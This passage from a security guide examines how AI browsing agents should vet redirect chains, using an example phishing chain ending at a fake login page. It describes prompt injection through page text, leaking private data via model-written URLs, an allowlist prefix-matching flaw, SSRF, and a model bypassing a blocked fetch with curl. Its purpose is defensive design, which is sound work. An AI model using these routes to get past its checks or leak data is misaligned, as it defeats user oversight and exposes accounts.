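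In-line checks also have drawbacks. Every server contacted before a check refuses a link receives the real visitor's network address and any cookies the browser holds for that server. The checks must also be quick, because the user is waiting. An advance check on an isolated machine can take a minute to examine a suspicious page without exposing the user's accounts. However, *Client-Side Zero-Shot LLM Inference for Comprehensive In-Browser URL Analysis* (2025) argues for analyzing pages in the user's own browser, partly for the same privacy reason that favors a self-hosted expander.

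Developers can add in-line checks only to tools they control, which excludes a fetcher that runs on a model provider's servers.

If the developer controls the tool, the in-line check should determine whether the agent may continue. An advance check can provide extra warnings, particularly for links that are already public and unlikely to trigger anything when opened. The software can block a link if the advance check finds a malicious page, but the in-line check is still necessary if the page looks harmless.

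Neither kind of check helps when the chain is what it appears to be but the last page is harmful. Zhang and colleagues note that attackers collect passwords through Google Forms, and the Discord attackers stored their malware on GitHub and other trusted services. If Ruth's agent is allowed to visit `docs.google.com`, a link to a fake login form there passes the host rules at every hop.

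## Where the checks belong in the agent's action loop

Software can intervene at several points during a single page visit, from when the model writes a URL to when it types something into the page. Later checks have more evidence about the link but can prevent less.

| Point in the visit | What a check can still prevent | What has already happened |
|---|---|---|
| The model proposes a URL | Private data leaving in the URL | Nothing outside the action loop |
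| Before the first request | Contact with a private address or a known malicious host | At most, a DNS lookup |
| At each hop | Contact with the next server | Earlier servers have received their requests |
| On arrival | The model reading the page or acting on it | The last server has the request, and a browser may have run the page's code |
| Before page text reaches the model | Prompt injection through that text | The page has loaded |
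| Before a password or payment | Loss of an account or money | The model has read the page, including any hidden instructions |

### When the model proposes a URL

At first, the URL is only text in the model's reply. The rule against leaking private data belongs here, before even a DNS lookup.

In a simple version of this check, the code editor Zed's agent shows the user each URL and waits for approval before fetching it. Irwin, in *Require confirmation for fetch tool*, explains that a prompt injection could otherwise trick the agent into putting private code or access keys in the URL.

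Google's agent in Chrome does more of this automatically. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a fixed rule that restricts URLs the model writes to known public ones, much like OpenAI's rule. When the agent tries to visit a new site, a second model called the User Alignment Critic checks whether the site is relevant to the user's task. The critic receives a description of the proposed action but no unfiltered page content, so a malicious page cannot give it instructions directly.

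### Before the first request

The next checks cover the host's form, network address and reputation. The WebFetch tool in Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, runs several of them. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* (2025) describes how the tool first limits the URL to about 2,000 characters, changes `http` to `https` and removes any user name or password. It then looks up the host on a blocklist.

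Anthropic's *Data usage* explains that the tool sends only the host name for this lookup. For Ruth's link, it would send `short.example`. This keeps the path and query private, but it means the blocklist could block either every link on that shortener or none of them.

WebFetch also applies the user's permission rules. According to Anthropic's *Tools reference*, a rule such as `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` can allow a domain, deny it, or require the user's approval each time. In Manual mode, the tool prompts the user about any domain without a rule, except for a built-in set of documentation sites.

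### At every hop

WebFetch follows redirects on the same host automatically. When a redirect leads to another host, the tool stops and returns a short text with the original URL and the new one. Claude then has to call WebFetch again, and the new host goes through the blocklist and permission rules like any other.

If Ruth used Claude Code, the four-hop version of her link would take four calls:

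| Call | URL that Claude requests | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `https://short.example/q7Xk` | A redirect to `click.example` |
| 2 | `https://click.example/mail/88` | The tool follows one redirect on the same host, then reports another to `docs.example.com` |
| 3 | The open redirect on `docs.example.com` | A redirect to `docs.example.com.attacker.example` |
| 4 | `https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login` | The fake login page, unless the blocklist or a permission rule stops the call |

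The checks before the fourth call run before the tool contacts the attacker's page. They work even if Ruth has told the tool not to ask again about `short.example`, because that approval doesn't cover later hosts in the redirect chain.

Handing control back to the model at each new host has two drawbacks. The model writes the next URL, so a model under an attacker's influence could add private data to it, and the check for leaks has to run again on every call. The redirect address is also text that a stranger chose, and its path could contain an instruction to the model. The AI SDK and Docker's fetch tool avoid both problems by checking and following redirects inside the tool.

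### On arrival

Tools that operate a browser often check the address again after the page has loaded. A copy of browser-use's security code, in a fork of the project, shows where Browser Use placed its checks:

```
before navigation:      if the URL is not allowed, cancel
after navigation:       if the page's URL is not allowed, close the tab
when a new tab opens:   if its URL is not allowed, close the tab
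```

According to a code comment, the second check is there "in case of redirects". The browser follows redirects by itself, so the code gets the final address only after navigation finishes. By then, the server at that address has received the request, and the page may have run its scripts. Closing the tab can keep the model from reading the page or typing into it, but it can't undo a leak or a request to a private machine. If the tab fails to close, the code only records an error.

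The copy also has a flaw in how it matches URLs. If a developer writes a list entry as a full address, such as `https://docs.example.com`, the code only tests whether the URL starts with that text, so the fake login page at `https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login` would pass both checks. It would not pass if the entry were written without the scheme, as `docs.example.com`.

Hermes Agent, an open-source agent, has a similar check for private addresses, described in hermes-agent's *fix(security): add SSRF protection to browser_navigate* (2026). The check examines the final URL after navigation. If a redirect led to `localhost` or a cloud metadata address, the browser switches to a blank page and the tool returns an error. This prevents the model from reading the internal page with its next command.

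Other browser tools leave larger gaps. Browserbase rents out cloud browsers that agents can control. Its *Allowed Domains* describes an experimental feature that lets developers limit the sites a session may navigate to. The feature checks only top-level navigations, which change the main page. It ignores frames, images, scripts and background requests, so a script on a permitted page could still send data to any host. Playwright MCP, which connects agents to the Playwright browser-control tool, has a list of allowed origins, but according to its documentation, the list "does not affect redirects".

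Chrome's protection for human users shows a better place for an arrival check. Chromium's *How Safe Browsing Lookup Interacts with Navigation* describes how the browser compares the first URL and every redirect with a list of known threats while the requests are under way. The servers still receive the requests, and the browser may finish downloading the response during the check, but it does not parse the page or run its code until the check is complete. An agent's browser could pause at the same point while other software decides whether the page should be parsed.

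### Before the page text reaches the model

A page on an approved host can still contain a prompt injection, for instance in a comment. Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* describes how the VS Code editor used to ask users for two approvals, first to contact the site and then to add the response to the conversation. If the domain was trusted, VS Code skipped the first approval but still required the second.

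That arrangement remains only in an older part of VS Code that Microsoft will remove in February 2027. In its replacement, the user approves only contact with the site, according to Microsoft's *Secure development with AI in VS Code*. Few people would read a whole page closely enough to find white text on a white background, so losing the user's review of the page probably matters little if software scans the text instead.

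Chrome's agent runs such a scan on every page it sees. A classifier looks for prompt injections while the main model works on its next step, and blocks actions based on content it judges to be an attack. Running the two in parallel saves time. The main model may have read the attack before the classifier finishes, but it hasn't acted on it. Parker acknowledges that the classifier can't catch everything.

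Claude gives WebFetch a URL and a question. A smaller model usually answers the question from the page text, and Claude receives only that answer. Anthropic presents this as a way to extract information, and it should not count as a security filter. The smaller model may drop an irrelevant instruction on the page, but an attacker could also try to get it to repeat one.

### Before a password or payment

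If Ruth's agent is allowed to visit `docs.google.com`, host checks won't stop a fake login form there, but a check just before the agent types her password can still protect it. Browser Use's hosted service lets a developer bind a password to particular hosts and types it only on those hosts. If Ruth's supplier password is bound to `docs.example.com`, the agent can't use this feature to enter it on Google's site or the attacker's.

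This check doesn't depend on the redirect chain, whether the page looks genuine, or the model's judgment. But the binding covers every subdomain of the host, so the developer should choose the narrowest host that works. Once the service has typed the password, the page can read it, and so can an agent that controls the browser. The check therefore can't protect the password from a malicious script on the correct site.

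Chrome's agent asks the user before it signs in with a saved password, and the model has no direct access to the password store. The agent also tries to stop before making a purchase or payment or sending a message. It asks the user before navigating to any site on a fixed list of sensitive sites, such as banks and medical services.

### A browser that refuses redirects

Websites can also have the browser enforce some of these rules. Connection Allowlists, which Google proposed, lets a site list the addresses that its own pages may contact. The server sends the list in a header when it delivers the page:

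```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://api.example.com/*")
```

`response-origin` means the origin that served the page, and the quoted pattern permits any path on `api.example.com`. The browser blocks all other connections from the page, including image loads, background requests and navigations.

By default, the browser also refuses redirects. Helme, in *Connection Allowlist*, gives the reason: once a request has gone out, the receiving server controls where it goes next, so a permitted first address guarantees nothing. A site can lift this restriction by adding a parameter:

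```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://api.example.com/*"); redirects=allow
```

Report URI, a company that collects browsers' security reports, says in its guide *Connection Allowlist* that redirects to unlisted destinations are refused by default. West's draft, *Connection Allowlists*, is stricter and specifies that any redirected request fails. Browser tests listed by Mozilla check that even a same-origin redirect fails. Developers should assume the stricter behavior until they have tested their own pages.

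West thinks a total ban is unlikely to satisfy developers and considers several alternatives. The browser could apply the list to every hop, or a site could mark particular entries as free to redirect, either anywhere or only to other addresses on the list. Report URI warns that with `redirects=allow`, a permitted host can redirect to a forbidden one, so the parameter does not check every hop.

Connection Allowlists became part of Chrome in version 152, dated August 25 (Google's *Chrome 152*, 2026), after a trial in versions 148 to 151 (Google's *Connection Allowlists origin trial*, 2026). Microsoft ran a separate trial for Edge, with an expiry date of September 8 (Microsoft's *Connection Allowlists*). In March, Chromium's *Intent to Experiment* (2026) recorded no position from the developers of Firefox or Safari. The specification is still an unofficial draft, and browsers not based on Chromium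 ignore the header.

Connection Allowlists would not protect Ruth's agent from the fake login page, because the site that serves a page also sets its allowlist, and the attacker has no reason to set one. The header is more useful on the page where an application displays the agent's answers. There, it could prevent the kind of leak Rehberger found in ChatGPT by blocking an image whose URL contains private data. Google also recommends it for pages that run AI-generated code.

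A strict allowlist can break legitimate features. Google's *FedCM* (2026) warns that users may be unable to sign in through an outside identity provider unless the site lists that provider's addresses. A related header, `Connection-Allowlist-Report-Only`, reports what the browser would have blocked, without blocking it, so developers can find these problems before enforcing the list.

### Who decides when the host changes

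A redirect to a new host may be routine or an attack, so the agent needs a way to decide whether to follow it. Fixed rules are quick and consistent. Their result should be final for private addresses, forbidden schemes and anything on a blocklist, because text on a web page can't change it. But fixed rules can't establish whether an unfamiliar invoicing site belongs to the supplier's new provider.

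Developers also need to check whether a tool's allowlist or denylist takes precedence. In VS Code's browser tools, a denied domain overrides an allowed one (GitHub (2026)). According to Browser Use's *All Parameters*, the allowlist takes precedence. If a developer allows `*.example.com` and denies `old.example.com`, VS Code will block `old.example.com`, but Browser Use will open it.

A model can judge whether a host fits the task, but the model doing the task may already have read the attacker's email, so a separate model with limited input, such as Chrome's critic, is safer. In VS Code's Assisted permissions setting, a model reviews each tool call and refers those it does not approve to the user. Microsoft cautions that this model can make mistakes. In Claude Code, sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans start in auto mode, where a classifier makes most of the decisions that would otherwise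 go to the user.

The user often has information that the rules and models lack, such as whether the supplier recently changed its billing system. But if the agent asked about every new host, it would ask many questions the user can't answer. Ruth has no reason to recognize `click.example`, and knowing that a link passes through it doesn't help her work out where the link ends.

It would be better to ask Ruth only about the destination. The tool would follow intermediate redirects under the fixed rules and discard any page text that came with them. When an unfamiliar host responds with an ordinary page, the tool would hold the page back and ask Ruth. This still sends the host a request, which reveals that somebody opened the link. For sensitive sites, and for URLs that the model composed, the tool has to ask before it sends the request.

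### What a useful question shows

Ordinary code should write the question shown to the user, because a model that has read the attacker's email could describe the link the way the attacker wants. The question should start with the part of the host that identifies its owner. In `docs.example.com.attacker.example`, that is `attacker.example`, which a narrow window might cut off. The question should also show where the link came from, which known site the user might expect, and what the agent intends to do on the page. If the model wrote the URL, the question should include the path and query too, since those could contain private data.

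How much a user's approval covers matters as much as how the prompt is worded. Microsoft says that in the current version of VS Code, approving `https://example.com` covers only that host over `https`, so the editor prompts again for a subdomain or for the unencrypted `http` address. WebFetch lets the user approve one fetch, approve the domain for the current project from then on, or refuse and tell Claude what to do instead. Lasting approval of a shortener is reasonable only if the tool separately checks the host it redirects to.

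The model must not be able to answer an approval prompt itself. GitHub describes this rule for VS Code's browser, where agents cannot approve website permissions on the user's behalf.

People stop reading even well-written questions when there are too many and most of the alarms are false. Claude Code's automatic default and VS Code's Assisted permissions both reduce interruptions, but neither is evidence that the classifier makes better decisions than an attentive user. For an agent like Ruth's, the fixed rules should settle nearly every link without involving her.

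### When a check fails

A checking service can be slow or unreachable, so developers have to choose whether the software then continues without the check ("fails open") or stops ("fails closed").

| Software | What goes wrong | What happens |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome's Safe Browsing check | No answer within 5 seconds | Navigation continues |
| Claude Code's WebFetch | The network blocks Anthropic's blocklist service | The fetch fails, unless the user has turned the check off |
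| Hermes Agent | The module that checks URLs won't load | The tool refuses every URL |

Chrome's choice makes sense for people, who would otherwise lose access to the whole web whenever Google's service had a fault. An agent can usually wait, try again or look elsewhere, so failing closed does less harm. The developer can limit the damage from an outage by running the rules about schemes, hosts and private addresses locally. When only the reputation service is down, the tool can still open sites the user already deals with and refuse unfamiliar ones.

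The model should also get a clear account of what happened. Before version 2.1.212, an error message from the service behind WebFetch's smaller model could reach Claude as if it were text from the page. A vague error can also lead the model to try again by another route. Claude Code has a command-line tool that can run `curl`, and a refusal from WebFetch doesn't by itself stop that tool from requesting the same URL, so the restriction has to apply to every tool with network access.

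Claude Code's web search limit shows one way to phrase a refusal. When Claude reaches the limit, the tool returns a notice to continue with the information it already has, rather than an error, which would invite another attempt. The notice for a blocked link could include that the URL is off limits and that the model may look for the invoice on the supplier's own site. Browserbase similarly keeps the session open after it blocks a navigation, so the agent can continue with permitted sites.

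### Caching and logs

Storing results saves time, but reusing a stored approval is riskier than reusing a stored page. WebFetch keeps a blocklist result for five minutes and a page for 15 minutes. Reusing a stored page sends no new request, so the server has no chance to change the content. With a stored approval, the agent makes a new request based on an old result. In the delayed attack on Ruth, the approval was 14 minutes old. A five-minute limit would have forced another check, but looking up only `short.example` again would not have revealed the new destination.

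For each hop, the tool should log the time, the URL, the status code, the Location header and the network address it connected to. It should also log which rule or person allowed the next request, and whether the first URL came from a message or from the model.

browser-use can save a file of all network traffic through its `record_har_path` setting, which records full details and page content by default. Chrome's agent shows the user a work log of its steps. That log helps someone who is watching, but an investigator also needs the redirects between the steps. Any detailed log can contain login cookies, password-reset links and private pages, so developers should restrict access to it and delete old entries.

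### Delay and cost

Suppose the genuine version of Ruth's link goes from `short.example` to two pages on `click.example`, then to the invoice on `docs.example.com`. This chain has four URLs and two changes of host. The estimate below assumes that a reputation lookup takes 0.1 seconds, an extra model call takes 3 seconds, and Ruth takes 10 seconds to answer a question. It also assumes that the model rereads 20,000 tokens (pieces of text) on each extra call, at $3 per million:

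20,000 × $3 ÷ 1,000,000 = $0.06 per call

The table applies these figures to 100 similar links:

| Policy | Added time | Extra model calls | Questions for Ruth |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed rules and a lookup for every URL | 40 seconds | 0 | 0 |
| The same, and back to the model at each new host | 10 minutes 40 seconds | 200, costing $12 | 0 |
| The same lookups, and a question at each new host | 34 minutes | 0 | 200 |
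| The same lookups, and a question only about unfamiliar destinations, here 5 of the 100 | 90 seconds | 0 | 5 |

The estimate excludes the fixed rules because they take so little time. Even with the lookups, they add 0.4 seconds per link. browser-use's default pauses for page loading and between actions total 1.25 seconds if they run one after another, so users are unlikely to notice the extra delay.

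The lookups could also run at the same time as the requests, as they do in Chrome, which would hide most of the delay. But the agent would then contact each server before the lookup result came back. For an agent, avoiding that is worth a delay of 0.4 seconds.

Storing the repeated part of the conversation could make the extra model calls much cheaper, and a small separate model would cost less than the main one. The 200 questions would still be the worst part of the third policy. A full ReDence investigation of all 100 links would take more than an hour.

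### Decisions for Ruth's link

The fourth policy suits Ruth's agent. Her developer could treat a host as known if it appears in her address book or on an invoice she has already paid. The tool would apply the fixed rules to every URL and allow at most ten redirects. These are the decisions it would make:

| Situation | Example | What the tool does | What Ruth sees |
|---|---|---|---|
| Same host | `click.example/mail/88` redirects to `click.example/go/88` | Follows the redirect | Nothing |
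| Known new host | The chain reaches `docs.example.com/invoices/1042` | Follows it without the previous host's credentials, and marks the page text as untrusted | A summary of the invoice |
| Unknown host | The chain ends at `billing.example.net/1042` | Holds the page back and asks | The new host, the sender and the supplier's usual site |
| Unknown host that imitates a known one | `docs.example.com.attacker.example/login` | Refuses before sending a request | A warning that the link does not lead to her supplier |
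| Private address | `http://192.168.0.10/admin` | Refuses before connecting, with no option to continue | A notice that the link pointed into the office network |
| Too many hops | An eleventh redirect | Stops and treats the destination as unknown | A suggestion to get the invoice from the supplier's site |
| Check unavailable | The reputation service fails twice | Opens known hosts if they pass the local rules, and refuses unknown ones | For a refused link, the reason and an offer to try later |
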